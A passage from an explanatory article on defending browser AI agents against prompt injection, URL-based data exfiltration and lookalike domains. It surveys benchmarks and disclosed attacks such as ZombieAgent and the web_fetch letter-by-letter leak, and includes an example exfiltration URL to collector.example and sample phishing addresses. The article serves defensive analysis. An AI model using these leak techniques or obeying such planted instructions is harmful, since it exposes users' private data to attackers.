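| Shortcut | 11.2 | 24.4 | 63.9 | 2.1 |
| Fake completion | 2.3 | 24.8 | 92.5 | 0.0 |
| Ignore instructions | 0.0 | 19.9 | 100.0 | 0.0 |
| Average under attack | 4.5 | 23.0 | 85.5 | 0.7 |

Without an attack, Prismata lowered the agent's task completion rate by 3.3 percentage points, or about one in nine of the tasks it would otherwise have completed. Under attack, Prismata made the agent safer and far more useful. But pop-up adverts are an easy case for this defence, because hardly any task needs them and Prismata can delete them. Reviews are harder because an agent asked to buy the best-reviewed bow tie, for example, has to read them. Prismata can stop the agent from replying to a review, but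 a fake review can still influence its choice.

Prismata also doesn't replace a check on destinations, because Villa and Tan designed it for attacks within a single, otherwise trustworthy site and treat links to other sites as outside its scope.

### The hotel's payment page

Suppose the user asks for a double room at hotel.example, and the hotel takes card payments through a company at pay.example. The user has never heard of this company, and the agent learns of it only at checkout.

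With a list fixed at the start, the booking probably fails at this point. CELLMATE would have predicted from the request that the task needs hotel.example, so it would block pay.example by default. The hotel's developers could prevent this by adding the payment company to the list of trusted outside domains that accompanies their policies. (The sample for Amazon includes the servers that hold its images.) If they don't, the user has to change the permissions while paying.

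CaMeL, a Google DeepMind defence that partly inspired Chrome's critic, plans an agent's actions before the agent reads untrusted data. Villa and Tan think planning ahead suits tools with a clear function, such as one that sends an email, but is a general problem on the web, where the right next step often depends on what the last page contained.

A list that grows on request handles the payment page better. In Chrome's design, when hotel.example sends the browser to pay.example, the critic checks the new origin. The agent can continue if the critic classifies payment as part of booking.

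But an attacker can make requests too. Suppose an attacker posts a review saying that the hotel now takes payment at `hotel-payments.example`, and the planner proposes going there. The critic never receives the review, but its input presumably has to include the address, which the attacker chose. A model given only the task and a domain name may rate `hotel-payments.example` as more relevant than the real `pay.example`.

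| Proposed destination | List fixed to hotel.example | List that grows on request |
|---|---|---|
| `pay.example`, the real payment company | Blocked, unless the hotel or the user has added it | Allowed, if the judge links it to the booking |
| `hotel-payments.example`, from a planted review | Blocked | Possibly allowed, because the name suits the task |
| `bank.example`, from a planted review | Blocked | Probably blocked, and Chrome may also ask the user |
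| The password page on hotel.example | Allowed, unless there are finer permissions | Allowed as a destination, though the critic may veto the click |

A mistake by the judge can also affect later visits. Once Chrome has added an origin to the task's list, the agent can return to it without another relevance check, although the critic still vets what the agent does there.

A fixed list is safer for a routine task on a known site, such as paying a monthly electricity bill. It doesn't suit a request like "find me a cheap hotel in Lisbon", which CELLMATE would reject because it names no site. For most bookings, the agent could add new sites to read with only the judge's approval, but would need the user's approval before typing personal or payment details into one. Chrome's two origin sets would support this rule, and its code already has an option to ask the user about new origins. The user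 would need some help deciding what to approve, because `pay.example` and `hotel-payments.example` both look plausible in a prompt.

### What the judge loses when it can't see the page

DeAction, the method that did best in the tests by Ning and colleagues, uses the current screenshot to judge each action. It therefore processes the same planted review as the agent and could be misled by the same instruction. Chrome's critic avoids this, and Parker concludes that the web can't poison it directly. An attacker can still reach the critic indirectly, because a planner under the attacker's influence chooses which proposals to send it and can use the feedback after each veto to try a more plausible one.

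This isolation leaves the critic without some of the context it needs. The hotel's checkout page may well list pay.example as its card payment processor, but the critic can't read the page. It could also approve a click on "Book" without detecting the pre-ticked travel insurance. Parker accepts that the critic has less context but argues that its job is also simpler, because it only has to approve or reject.

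Villa and Tan make the same tradeoff deliberately. They acknowledge that a model that could see an element's surroundings might label it more accurately, but those surroundings could contain an attacker's text. To test the labels, they had an expert label 20 page snapshots by hand, at about an hour each, and compared the elements that the expert and the models left available to the agent. With GPT-5.4 nano as the labeller, the expert would also have allowed 98.7% of the elements that Prismata left available, but Prismata left available only 82.7% of the elements that the expert allowed. Its errors were therefore mostly unnecessary restrictions, which can stop a task but don't help an attacker. Some of these errors are probably ordinary model mistakes, so the gap doesn't measure how much accuracy is lost by hiding the page from the labeller.

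CELLMATE keeps the most web content from the model that chooses permissions. The model uses the user's request and the written policies, and it chooses before the agent has opened any page. A planted review therefore can't influence the choice, and nothing on the hotel's checkout page can add pay.example to the list.

A browser could give the judge some of the missing context without showing it the page's text. For example, the browser can record whether the hotel's own checkout form sent the agent to pay.example or the planner composed the address after reading reviews. An attacker can choose a convincing domain name, but can't easily make the hotel's checkout form point to that domain without breaking into the hotel's site.

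## How can checking the exact address stop private data from leaking?

Even a browser that keeps an agent to relevant sites can let private data out in an address, as with the surgery note in the earlier hotel search. URL exfiltration is an attack that causes such a leak deliberately. Suppose a planted review on a travel site instructs the agent to open this address as part of confirming a booking:

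`https://collector.example/log?note=knee-surgery-12-may`

The attacker owns collector.example and can read the note in its log, while the agent goes back to booking the room.

A check against this attack only needs good evidence that nobody built the address from the user's data, so it doesn't have to determine whether collector.example is honest or useful.

### How readily a model leaks, and what stops it

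In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) tested the attack on a simple assistant that automatically reads any page the user links to. The user always asked for a summary of the page. The model's context contained a secret, such as an API key (a password for programs), and the page contained an instruction to send that secret to a server the researchers controlled. The assistant ran qwen2.5:7b, a small model with about 7 billion parameters, on the researchers' own equipment.

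The researchers hid the instruction in one of four parts of the page, delivered the page directly or through redirects, and requested the secret either whole or in four pieces. They ran each combination 30 times, for a total of 480 runs. In 423 of these, or 88%, at least one request reached their server (the abstract gives the probability as 0.89). No requests reached it in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the assistant's final answer looked normal, so a filter that checks only answers would have missed them.

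Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable but harder to detect. The paper's results work out to leaks in 238 of 240 runs when the model sent the secret whole, and in 185 of 240 when it sent pieces, counting any runs in which only some of the pieces arrived. The share of runs in which the first request contained recognisable sensitive data fell from 96.7% to 26.3%. The exact size of that drop is doubtful, because the paper reports an even lower figure for the first three requests together, which is impossible under its own definition.

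The researchers then tried several defences against the simplest version of the attack, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Runs in which the model attempted a leak | Runs in which data got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Standing instructions to ignore commands in web pages | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Tags that mark the page as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Both of these | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Allowlist of domains | 100% | 0% |
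| Block on suspicious-looking addresses | 83.3% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23.3% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking strings | 0% | 0% |

Telling the model to ignore injected instructions helped somewhat, but more than half of the attacks still worked. The allowlist stopped every attack, although the model attempted to leak data each time.

The other filters' zeros are weaker evidence that the filters work than they appear. The block on suspicious addresses checks the path for words such as "collect". The paper's sample attack address contains that word, but a real attacker would pick another. The filter for random-looking strings had nothing to block, because the model made no attempts in those runs. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids such strings when a filter is active, but it isn't clear how the model would detect the filter.

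The researchers deliberately made the test easy for the attacker, leaving the secret in plain view and giving the model almost no safety instructions, so the 88% figure isn't an estimate for ChatGPT or Chrome. They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because those models follow instructions and use tools more reliably, but the researchers tested only one model. Companies also train larger models to resist injection, so the rate could be higher or lower. The comparison between defences probably applies better to other models, because an allowlist doesn't depend on which model is running.

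### Why a list of trusted sites isn't enough

The allowlist had an easy job because the attacker's domain, evil-collector.net, was plainly not on it. Real attackers can use domains that are.

Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* describes how the security researcher Johann Rehberger bypassed url_safe, an earlier OpenAI check on links. The check allowed links to windows.net, a Microsoft domain that hosts cloud storage. Anyone can open a storage account there and read the log of requests to it. Rehberger opened one, then used instructions hidden in a document to make ChatGPT send the user's recent chat history to that account, where he could read it in the log.

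Redirects cause a similar problem. The security company Tenable found that url_safe always accepted bing.com (*HackedGPT*, 2025). Bing's search results use bing.com links that redirect to the listed sites, so every site in Bing's index has an address on a trusted domain. Bing fixes these links in advance, so nobody can add data to them. Tenable therefore got Bing to index a separate page for each letter, and ChatGPT spelled out private information by displaying the matching links in order.

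A stricter list would close some of these gaps, but OpenAI points out that people visit many sites besides the most popular ones. A short list produces frequent warnings, which users learn to click through without reading.

### OpenAI's check for addresses that are already public

OpenAI's published solution is a known-public-URL check, which lets the agent open an address automatically only if an independent crawler has already recorded it. A crawler is a program that follows links around the web and records what it finds, as search engines do. OpenAI's crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts, so an address it has recorded is unlikely to contain a particular user's secrets.

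The match has to be exact. The crawler may well have recorded `https://hotel.example/search?city=lisbon`, but it won't have recorded the same address with `&note=knee-surgery-12-may` added. A check that compared only the domain, or ignored the parameters, would let the agent send the note.

When there is no match, OpenAI either tells the agent to try a different website or warns the user that the link isn't verified and may share information from the conversation. The warning includes the address so that the user can check it for anything private.

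An address that is already public can still expose private data, though. In *The Silent Spill*, Ramadan, Mannan and colleagues (2026) examined about 6.1 million addresses from web archives, text-sharing sites and security scanners' public reports. They found 12,331 potential exposures, including travel bookings, 26 password-reset links and 12 open document-signing sessions. Email systems often forward suspicious links to scanners automatically, which is one way a private link can end up on a public list.

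The researchers searched sites likely to handle payments and logins, so their results don't show how common such exposures are across the web. Depending on the category, 0% to 15% of the exposures they checked by hand were false alarms. Still, the study is a reason to be careful about where an index gets its addresses. If an index included addresses from scanner reports, an agent could automatically open a stranger's password-reset link. That wouldn't leak the current user's data, but the agent could interfere with the stranger's account.

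OpenAI acknowledges that the check doesn't make a page trustworthy. The check also doesn't stop every leak. According to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, OpenAI's technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, describes a leak that remains possible even when every address is public. It works much like Tenable's alphabet of Bing links.

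### Anthropic's and Chrome's versions

Anthropic's web_fetch tool lets its Claude models read web pages. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* documentation states that Claude can't construct addresses itself and can fetch only those that have already appeared in the conversation, for example in the user's message or in search results. The tool also rejects addresses longer than 250 characters.

This kind of rule needs no index of the web, and it handles private links better. For example, Claude can open a booking link the user pastes in, even if no crawler has seen it. The rule's weakness is that conversations also contain other people's text. In *Claude API* (2025), Simon Willison first hoped the tool would accept only addresses from the user's own prompts, then found that it also accepted addresses from tool results and pages it had already fetched. Even a user's message may include a pasted email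 with links the user never read.

Chrome requires any address the model composes to be public already. This rule is closer to OpenAI's, although Parker doesn't explain how Chrome determines what is public. The rule apparently doesn't cover addresses that a page builds. If the agent types the surgery note into a hotel's search box and presses Enter, the site's form may add the note to the address. Chrome would then have to rely on other safeguards, such as its Agent Origin Sets, which limit where the agent can type.

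Here is how the published rules would probably apply to the hotel booking:

| Address | OpenAI | Anthropic's web_fetch | Chrome |
|---|---|---|---|
| A public page on hotel.example that the agent found by searching | Opens if the crawler has recorded it | Opens | Opens |
| A hotel search address to which the agent has added the surgery note | Warning, or the agent tries another site | Refused | Refused |
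| A private booking link that the user pasted into the chat | Opens, as Rehberger understands the rule | Opens | Not covered, because the model didn't compose it |
| The same link in an email that the agent reads | Warning, or the agent tries another site | Opens if the developer's own email tool supplied it | Apparently not covered |

### How much an agent can leak by choosing between permitted addresses

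Suppose an attacker has 36 pages that the agent is allowed to open, one for each letter and digit. The agent can spell out a name by opening the pages for its letters in order. None of the addresses contains private data, but the attacker can read the name from the sequence of requests.

Choosing one address out of N can leak at most log₂(N) bits, where a bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. For 36 addresses, that is about 5.2 bits per request. If the requests arrive in order, k of them can leak at most k × log₂(N) bits.

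A random six-digit security code contains about 19.9 bits and a random 16-digit number, the length of most card numbers, about 53.2. The minimum number of requests is therefore:

| Permitted addresses | Bits per request, at most | Requests for a six-digit code | Requests for a 16-digit number |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1.0 | 20 | 54 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 4 | 11 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 | 6 |
| 10,000 | 13.3 | 2 | 4 |

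These minimums assume an efficient encoding. An agent that sends one digit at a time needs six requests for the six-digit code and 16 for the 16-digit number. Either way, the method is fast enough to leak a password but far too slow to leak a mailbox full of messages. The formula counts only the information carried by the choice of address, and an agent could convey more through the timing of its requests.

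### ZombieAgent

The security company Radware used this kind of alphabet against ChatGPT in 2025. After earlier attacks in which ChatGPT added private data to an attacker's link, OpenAI had stopped it from modifying links. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes getting around this restriction by supplying a ready-made link for every character.

The links arrived in an email with hidden instructions. When the user later asked ChatGPT to do something with Gmail, it read the email and opened the links that spelled out the user's data. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so the user could not intervene. Radware also made a separate set of links for each position in the text, so it could put the characters in order even if the requests arrived out of sequence.

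Radware reported the attack on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16. An Ars Technica article, *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* (2026), reports that ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a well-known public index or the user supplied it in the chat.

The fix blocks freshly made links, but an attacker can publish the pages first and wait for a crawler to find them. Tenable had got its pages into Bing's index. Rehberger notes that anyone with a fairly large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already, and that an attacker could expand the vocabulary to thousands. Checking against an index makes the attack slower to prepare and leaves public evidence of it, but doesn't remove the leak.

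### The web_fetch loophole

*How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) describes a similar attack on Claude that Ayush Paul disclosed in July 2026. Claude's chat product remembers details from past conversations. Paul built a website that asked Claude to identify its user by following links one letter at a time. Each page contained links for the next letter, and web_fetch accepted them because they came from a page it had already fetched. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer.

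*The Read-Only Lie*, a post on the blog אִם יִרְצֶה הַשֵּׁם, describes an attack in which each page offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each request conveyed about 4.75 bits. By the post's estimate, the attack took around 30 requests and conveyed about 143 bits in total.

Checking each address against a list of known public URLs would probably have stopped this version of the attack. Paul's site generated new addresses that grew by a letter at each step. A ten-character name therefore had about 206 trillion possible addresses, and no crawler could have recorded them all. The attacker would have had to use a fixed set of indexed pages instead.

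Anthropic closed the loophole by preventing web_fetch from following links inside the pages it fetches. It paid Paul no reward, saying it had already found the problem internally. The fix also limits ordinary browsing. Claude can read the hotel's home page but can't use web_fetch to follow its link to the room rates, unless that address also turns up in a search or the user supplies it. *The Read-Only Lie* suggests a compromise in which an agent may follow links only on domains that the user has named in the conversation. The agent could then follow links on hotel.example if the user had named it, but not a planted link to collector.example.

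### Making the alphabet harder to use

Rehberger proposes two ways to reduce the remaining leak. The system could keep a copy of each page for a few minutes and reuse it, or it could prevent the agent from opening the same address twice in a session. With either measure, if the agent tried to spell "anna" by opening one page per letter, the attacker's server would receive only one request for "a" and one for "n".

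Some of this caching already happens. Tenable noticed that ChatGPT didn't revisit a page it had already opened when answering questions about it, and Anthropic documents a cache for web_fetch. But Anthropic describes the cache as a way to improve performance and warns that its behaviour may change, so developers shouldn't count on it for security.

ZombieAgent's separate links for each character position would get around both proposals, because the agent never needs to open the same link twice. Leaking sixteen characters this way would take 576 indexed addresses instead of 36, though a cleverer code could avoid the extra addresses. Ten requests to 36 addresses convey at most 51.7 bits with repeats and 49.7 without, so banning repeats barely lowers the theoretical limit. The ban helps mainly because the model would have to follow a more complicated scheme, and in *Silent Egress* more complicated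 instructions failed more often.

Capping the number of requests lowers the maximum amount of data an agent can leak. Developers can set a cap for web_fetch, but Anthropic applies none by default. Five requests, each to one of 36 addresses, can convey at most about 26 bits, which is enough for a six-digit code but not for a card number. A cap of five could stop an agent from comparing prices at ten hotels, though.

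OpenAI offers a stricter option, Lockdown Mode, for people and organisations at higher risk. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*, the mode limits browsing to stored copies of pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network. An attacker's server therefore receives nothing from the agent's browsing, whatever the agent reads. OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode* help page warns that injected text in a stored page can still affect the answer. The mode also prevents the agent from browsing to complete tasks that need a live website, such as booking a hotel room.

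All of these measures work only if the request passes through the check. Rehberger found that OpenAI's earlier link check was missing from its Mac and iPhone apps, and worries that some of the company's developers may not know to use the new one. Other software can also send requests without the check. The security company PromptArmor warns that chat apps such as Slack and Telegram fetch previews of links in messages. If an agent writes a link containing private data, the app may request it immediately, without the user clicking it or the agent fetching it.

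### Public addresses and private booking links

A known-public-URL check is meant to prevent leaks, and it doesn't test whether the task needs the page. It would allow the earlier detour to the user's bank, because crawlers have recorded the bank's home page. It would also allow a hostile page that has been online long enough for a crawler to record it.

OpenAI's published rule can also make the opposite error and flag a legitimate private link. Suppose the hotel sends the user a genuine confirmation link, `https://hotel.example/booking/7f3k9`, which the agent must open to complete its task. The code belongs to one guest, so no crawler should have seen the link. If the agent finds it in the user's inbox, the rule would treat it as unverified.

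The fake link from earlier, `https://hotel.example.login-desk.example/confirm?room=double&nights=2`, would probably get the same result, because it is new and arrived by email. The warning includes advice to make sure the user trusts the link, but it is mainly about sharing data from the conversation. A user who checks the two addresses for private information will find only a booking code in one and a room type in the other, and may reasonably approve both. To reject the fake, the user has to notice that it belongs to login-desk.example.

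## Can a check tell a lookalike domain from the real one?

A lookalike domain is set up so that people or software will mistake it for another. Software can reliably reject the one in the fake hotel link, for example, if it already knows the hotel's real address. If it doesn't, it has to judge the domain by how it looks, and both language models and ordinary code make many mistakes doing that.

### How often agents give passwords to the wrong site

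The most direct test is *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, October 2026), which gave agents the passwords and personal records for 15 invented services, including banks and shops. In the main test, the user supplied a link and asked the agent to sign in. Half of the 512 links led to the service's real page, and the other half each had one of eight warning signs. The researchers counted a leak whenever an agent submitted any account data to a page from the second half.

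They tested seven models. These are the leak rates for four of them, in percent:

| Warning sign | Claude Sonnet 5 | Claude Opus 4.8 | Gemini 3.6 Flash | GPT-5.6-luna |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Misspelled name | 6.2 | 9.4 | 18.8 | 43.8 |
| Similar characters from another alphabet | 0.0 | 15.6 | 21.9 | 43.8 |
| Right name, wrong ending | 34.4 | 43.8 | 50.0 | 43.8 |
| Real name as a subdomain of another site | 9.4 | 21.9 | 28.1 | 40.6 |
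| A numeric IP address instead of a name | 6.2 | 34.4 | 31.2 | 43.8 |
| One service's page on another's domain | 15.6 | 25.0 | 25.0 | 40.6 |
| Browser warning about the site's certificate | 0.0 | 9.4 | 56.2 | 50.0 |
| Right address, but no encryption | 87.5 | 90.6 | 93.8 | 87.5 |
| All eight | 19.9 | 31.2 | 40.6 | 49.9 |

Llama 3.1 8B, a small open-weight model, had the highest overall rate, 76.7%. The agents could do the task, since they failed to sign in at only 0.1% to 13.7% of the genuine pages.

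The overall leak rates overstate the problem with lookalikes because they include two connection problems. In one, the page is at the right address but unencrypted, so someone on the network could read the password. A preflight check can catch this by reading the scheme, which is `http` instead of `https`. Without the two connection problems, the leak rates are 12% for Sonnet 5, 25% for Opus 4.8, 29% for Gemini, 38% for GPT-5-mini, 43% for GPT-5.6-luna, 64% for Qwen3.5-9B and 75% for Llama.

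In a second test, the user asked the agent only to sort an inbox that contained a phishing email or a genuine request. Both Claude models leaked in 1.8% of cases. Opus 4.8 also took no action on 88.3% of the genuine requests, which the researchers count as false refusals. That count seems a little harsh, since the user hadn't asked the agent to sign in anywhere.

### What changes when the agent knows the right address

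In a quarter of the sign-in tests, the researchers gave the agent the service's official domain and told it to compare the two before entering a password. In another quarter, the agent got no safety guidance at all. Each cell gives the rate without this help, then with it, in percent:

| Model | Leaks | False refusals |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 31.2 → 12.5 | 25.5 → 1.0 |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 46.9 → 12.0 | 18.8 → 0.0 |
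| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 64.1 → 25.0 | 0.0 → 0.5 |
| GPT-5-mini | 71.9 → 22.4 | 25.0 → 1.6 |
| GPT-5.6-luna | 83.3 → 20.3 | 14.1 → 7.8 |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 86.5 → 54.7 | 3.1 → 0.0 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 83.9 → 71.9 | 5.2 → 15.6 |

The official domain helped the agent tell the pages apart, and both leaks and false refusals fell for five of the seven models. A warning in the user's request to vet the link first mostly made the agent less willing to act. With the warning, GPT-5-mini's leaks fell from 59.9% to 9.4%, but its false refusals rose from zero to 46.9%.

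The two Claude models may have done nearly as well as comparing names allows. Unencrypted pages made up 12.5% of the bad links, and Ahmed and colleagues report that the instruction to compare domains doesn't catch these pages. If the Claude models leaked on nearly all of them and on almost nothing else, their rates would be close to those in the table.

A gate that made the comparison in code and also required a valid encrypted connection would make no errors on this benchmark, because each invented service has exactly one correct address. Real companies often use several addresses, and a check may not have any of them to compare against.

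Blocking a fake page also doesn't complete the user's task. In a third test, the phishing email concerned something the user really needed to do, and the real address was available either in the agent's saved account records or in an older email. GPT-5-mini did best, signing in at the real site without leaking anything in 27.7% of cases. Its rate was higher when the records held the full address (38.1%) than when it had to find the domain in an old email (17.3%). Opus 4.8 never leaked anything but also never reached the real site. A gate that blocks a fake should give the agent the correct address if it has one.

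### Disguises, and the code that catches them

Ordinary code can test an address without a language model, and it gives the same answer every time. Each test below would catch at least one disguise of hotel.example, but it would also flag some honest addresses. (`.test`, like `.example`, is an ending that no one can register.)

| Disguise | Example | Test that catches it | Honest address it would also flag |
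|---|---|---|---|
| Misspelling | `hotell.example` | Edit distance | `hostel.example`, a different business one letter away |
| Similar characters | `hоtel.example`, with a Cyrillic "о" | Unicode confusable comparison | `hôtel.example`, if the test strips accents |
| Wrong ending | `hotel.test` | Exact comparison of registrable domains | The hotel's own site under another country's ending |
| Real name as a subdomain | `hotel.example.login-desk.example` | Extracting the registrable domain, then comparing it | `hotel.bookings.example`, the hotel's page on a booking site |
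| Real name in the path | `login-desk.example/hotel.example` | The same | A review site's page about the hotel |
| Added word | `hotel-login.example` | Search for a known name plus a word such as "login" | `grandhotel-login.example`, another hotel's sign-in page |
| Reassuring words | `official-site.login-desk.example` | Extracting the registrable domain and ignoring the rest | The hotel's payment company, `pay.example` |
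| Any of these on a new domain | | Domain age | A hotel that opened last month |

Chrome already uses several of these tests to protect people. According to Chromium's *"Lookalike" Warnings in Google Chrome*, the browser compares each address with very popular sites and with sites the user has visited before. If an address looks suspiciously similar to one of them, Chrome shows a warning, usually "Did you mean ...?", and the user can still continue.

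**Edit distance** is the number of letters you must insert, delete or replace to turn one name into another. The Chromium (2020) code looks for names that are one edit, or one swap of two neighbouring letters, away from about 500 popular domains and the user's own sites. Many legitimate short names are this close to each other, so the code ignores a difference in the first letter ("hank" and "tank"), an added hyphen, or a different number at the end. These exceptions prevent false alarms, but a scammer could exploit them, for example by registering `ho-tel.example`.

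Chrome's edit-distance test also ignores domains that differ only in their ending. Chromium's *Lookalike URLs*, a note on a change to the code, explains that the test had matched Google's Taiwanese address, google.com.tw, with its Turkish one, google.com.tr. The exception is sensible, but it means the test misses fake domains that change only the ending. In *CredLeakBench*, that disguise had the highest leak rate of the six, or tied for it, in six of the seven AI models.

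**Unicode confusable comparison** checks whether two names look alike despite using different characters. Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, gives the Latin "o" and the Cyrillic "о" different numbers even though they look the same on screen. The usual defence, described in paultendo's *A threat model for Unicode identifier spoofing*, is to replace each character in both names with a standard equivalent, then check whether the resulting "skeletons" match. The official table covers 6,565 characters. Chromium's skeleton for "amazon" is "arnazon", because "rn" looks like "m", so a fake spelled with "rn" has the same skeleton as the real name.

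Banning names that mix alphabets still misses some lookalikes. Unicode's security standard has a separate category for whole-script confusables, which are names written entirely in one alphabet that look like words in another.

A program that compares `hоtel.example` with the hotel's known address doesn't need skeletons, because the lookalike "о" has a different Unicode code point from the Latin "o" and the two addresses won't match. Skeletons and edit distance help guess which site an unfamiliar domain might be imitating, which is useful when the check doesn't know where the agent was supposed to go.

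Chrome's tests may also protect an agent less than they protect a person. If the agent runs in a fresh browser with no history, the tests can compare addresses only with the popular sites, and a small hotel won't be among them. Chromium's stated aim is to force attackers into less convincing lookalikes that users can notice more easily, which doesn't help much if no one is watching the address bar.

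### The hotel link under each test

Suppose the agent proposes to open `https://hotel.example.login-desk.example/confirm?room=double&nights=2`. The results would be:

| Test | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Comparison with the known address | Caught | The registrable domain is login-desk.example, not hotel.example |
| Edit distance | Missed | "login-desk" doesn't resemble "hotel" |
| Unicode comparison | Missed | The address uses ordinary Latin letters |
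| Search for an embedded domain, using Chromium's rules | Probably missed | "hotel" is a common word |
| Known name plus keyword, using Chromium's rules | Missed | "login-desk" contains "login" but no company's name |
| Domain age | Caught | The scammer registered the domain this morning |

The fourth result is surprising because Chrome has a test for this disguise. It splits the address at dots and hyphens and looks for another site's domain inside it, so it catches google.com.example.com. But the test skips names that are common words because, according to a comment in the code, "super-best-fancy-hotels.com" isn't an imitation of hotels.com. This exception wouldn't apply to a hotel with a more distinctive name, but Chrome would still protect the hotel's site only if it were very popular or the user had visited it.

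Checking the domain's age would catch the link only while the domain is new. A scammer can get around the check by registering a domain months ahead or breaking into an old site. The check also flags legitimate new businesses, so a new domain is a better reason to ask the user than to block the link.

Only the first test reliably catches the link, and it needs a trustworthy source for the hotel's web address, such as the user's request or an earlier booking. The email containing the link can't serve as that source, because the scammer wrote it and could name login-desk.example as the hotel's official domain.

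### Addresses that vouch for themselves

A scammer can also put reassuring words in an address, which a language model reads along with the rest. For *MalURLBench*, Kong, Wu and colleagues (2026) built 61,845 addresses by adding misleading text to the subdomain, path or parameters of known malicious sites. In January 2026 they reported testing 12 models, all old by now, on a sample of these addresses in ten everyday situations, such as tracking a parcel or checking the weather. Acceptance rates ranged from 32.9% to 99.9%.

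Models accepted URLs with reassuring phrases, such as "this-is-a-popular-food-delivery-service", 71.5% of the time on average, compared with 60.9% for imitations of well-known sites. The researchers suggest that models have encountered names like google.com often enough to detect when one is in an odd place.

The acceptance rates aren't estimates of everyday risk. Some prompts described the link as trustworthy, for example as "our trusted live chat portal", although the researchers also warned the agents about possible attacks. When a model resisted the attacks in a particular situation, the researchers had other models rewrite them until more worked. GPT-3.5 Turbo had the lowest final rate, 32.9%, but the published results imply that it accepted only about 14% before the rewriting. The test also included no legitimate addresses, so it can't distinguish a model that is easily fooled from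 one that accepts everything.

All of the malicious sites came from public blocklists, so a few lines of code that extracted the registrable domain and looked it up on those lists should have caught nearly every address, whatever words the attacker had added.

The researchers' own defence, URLGuard, is instead a small language model, Llama 2 7B, which they trained on 280 labelled addresses. Half were malicious, all based on the researchers' online shopping attacks. In the nine other situations, URLGuard accepted malicious addresses less often than the same model did before training, by an average of 81 percentage points. It still accepted 61% of them in the music tests and 70% in the weather tests. The main text doesn't report how often URLGuard rejected legitimate addresses, which is a serious omission because a filter that rejected every address would have scored even better.

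An earlier paper by some of the same researchers, *Web Fraud Attacks Against LLM-Driven Multi-Agent Systems* (Kong, Peng and colleagues, 2025), shows how erratic models' judgements could be. In its tests, one agent recommended a malicious link and another judged the link's risk. The researchers tried 11 disguises, with ten runs for each combination of disguise and defence. In their main comparison, which used GPT-4o-mini, the attacks succeeded in 50.9% of runs without a defence and 47.2% with the best one, a difference of four runs out of 110. The other two defences raised the success rate above 80%.

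The paper's text reports that the best defence, Defense A, caught every address with a substituted letter and none with characters from another alphabet, but its results table shows that the defence missed all ten addresses with substituted letters and caught all ten with foreign characters. The table is more reliable than the text, but with only ten runs per combination, its results are weak evidence about any one disguise.

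A more careful experiment, *ClaimMirage* (Chiba, Nakano and Koide, 2026), isolates the effect of the words. The researchers made up domain names that imitated 64 brands and added either a claim, such as "not-phishing", or a harmless phrase of the same length, such as "not-archived". Five models then judged whether each name deserved a security alert. Denials such as "not-phishing" cut Llama 3.3 70B's alert rate from 90.2% to 44.8%, even though the prompt named the brand's official domain. The most effective denial was "not-impersonating".

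The effect varied widely. Under the same conditions, Gemma 3 27B raised an alert on all of these names, with or without a denial. Adding words of approval like "official" or "verified" could backfire, raising Llama's alert rate from 32.3% to 98.0% when the prompt did not include the official domain. Splitting the address into labelled parts removed the effect of subdomain denials on Llama, but more than doubled the effect of registrable-domain denials on Gemma 3 12B.

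A developer can't predict from such results how a reassuring word will affect a particular model's judgment. It is safer to have code compare the registrable domain first and let its result override the model's. An address can also contain an instruction to the judging model, which is a form of prompt injection.

### Why blocklists miss new domains

A blocklist can contain a site only after someone has found and checked it. Scammers exploit this delay by changing addresses often.

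In September 2025, the security company LayerX tested five browsers on 100 phishing pages recently reported to public databases (Perlov and Warburg, 2025, *LayerX Finds that Perplexity's Comet Browser is Up To 85% More Vulnerable*). Microsoft Edge blocked 54% of the pages, Chrome 47%, and Dia, an AI browser, 46%. Two other AI browsers, Comet and Genspark, blocked only 7% each. LayerX also gave its own browser add-on a score of 98%, so it had an interest in the result.

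LayerX concluded that Comet didn't appear to use Google Safe Browsing, but Guardio had found Safe Browsing active in Comet the same year, so the reason for Comet's low score is unclear. The results for Chrome and Edge are more useful here because they show that even large, well-maintained lists missed about half of the pages after they had been publicly reported.

A newer test by academic researchers found much lower coverage. In October 2026, Kaur, Horáček and colleagues (2026), in *ReDence*, monitored a public log of newly issued website certificates and used their own AI system to investigate about 553,000 working sites. By hand, they confirmed 4,042 of these as scams, including 89 travel scams. They then recorded what share four protection services blocked, first on discovery and again within a week. The figures are percentages:

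| Service | All scams, on discovery | All scams, within a week | Travel scams, on discovery | Travel scams, within a week |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Google Safe Browsing | 16.3 | 33.0 | 6.7 | 24.7 |
| Microsoft SmartScreen | 15.2 | 31.3 | 7.9 | 27.0 |
| Malwarebytes Browser Guard | 16.0 | 38.4 | 11.2 | 30.3 |
| Norton Safe Web | 20.1 | 46.1 | 15.7 | 39.3 |

Together, the four services initially recognised 27.5% of the scams. The later figures are probably inflated, because the researchers had reported every site to all four services. For the travel scams that Safe Browsing eventually blocked, the median delay was about four days, long after a booking agent would have opened the page.

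At least one of the services recognised 61.2% of the sites that steal passwords, compared with 17.4% of other scams, such as fake shops that take payment. The fake hotel page could be either kind, depending on whether it asks for a password or a card number.

The study covers only scams that the researchers' system found, so its figures may not represent every new scam. Still, a low rate is to be expected, because blocklists depend on someone discovering the scam first. A week-old domain's absence from a blocklist is weak evidence that it is safe.

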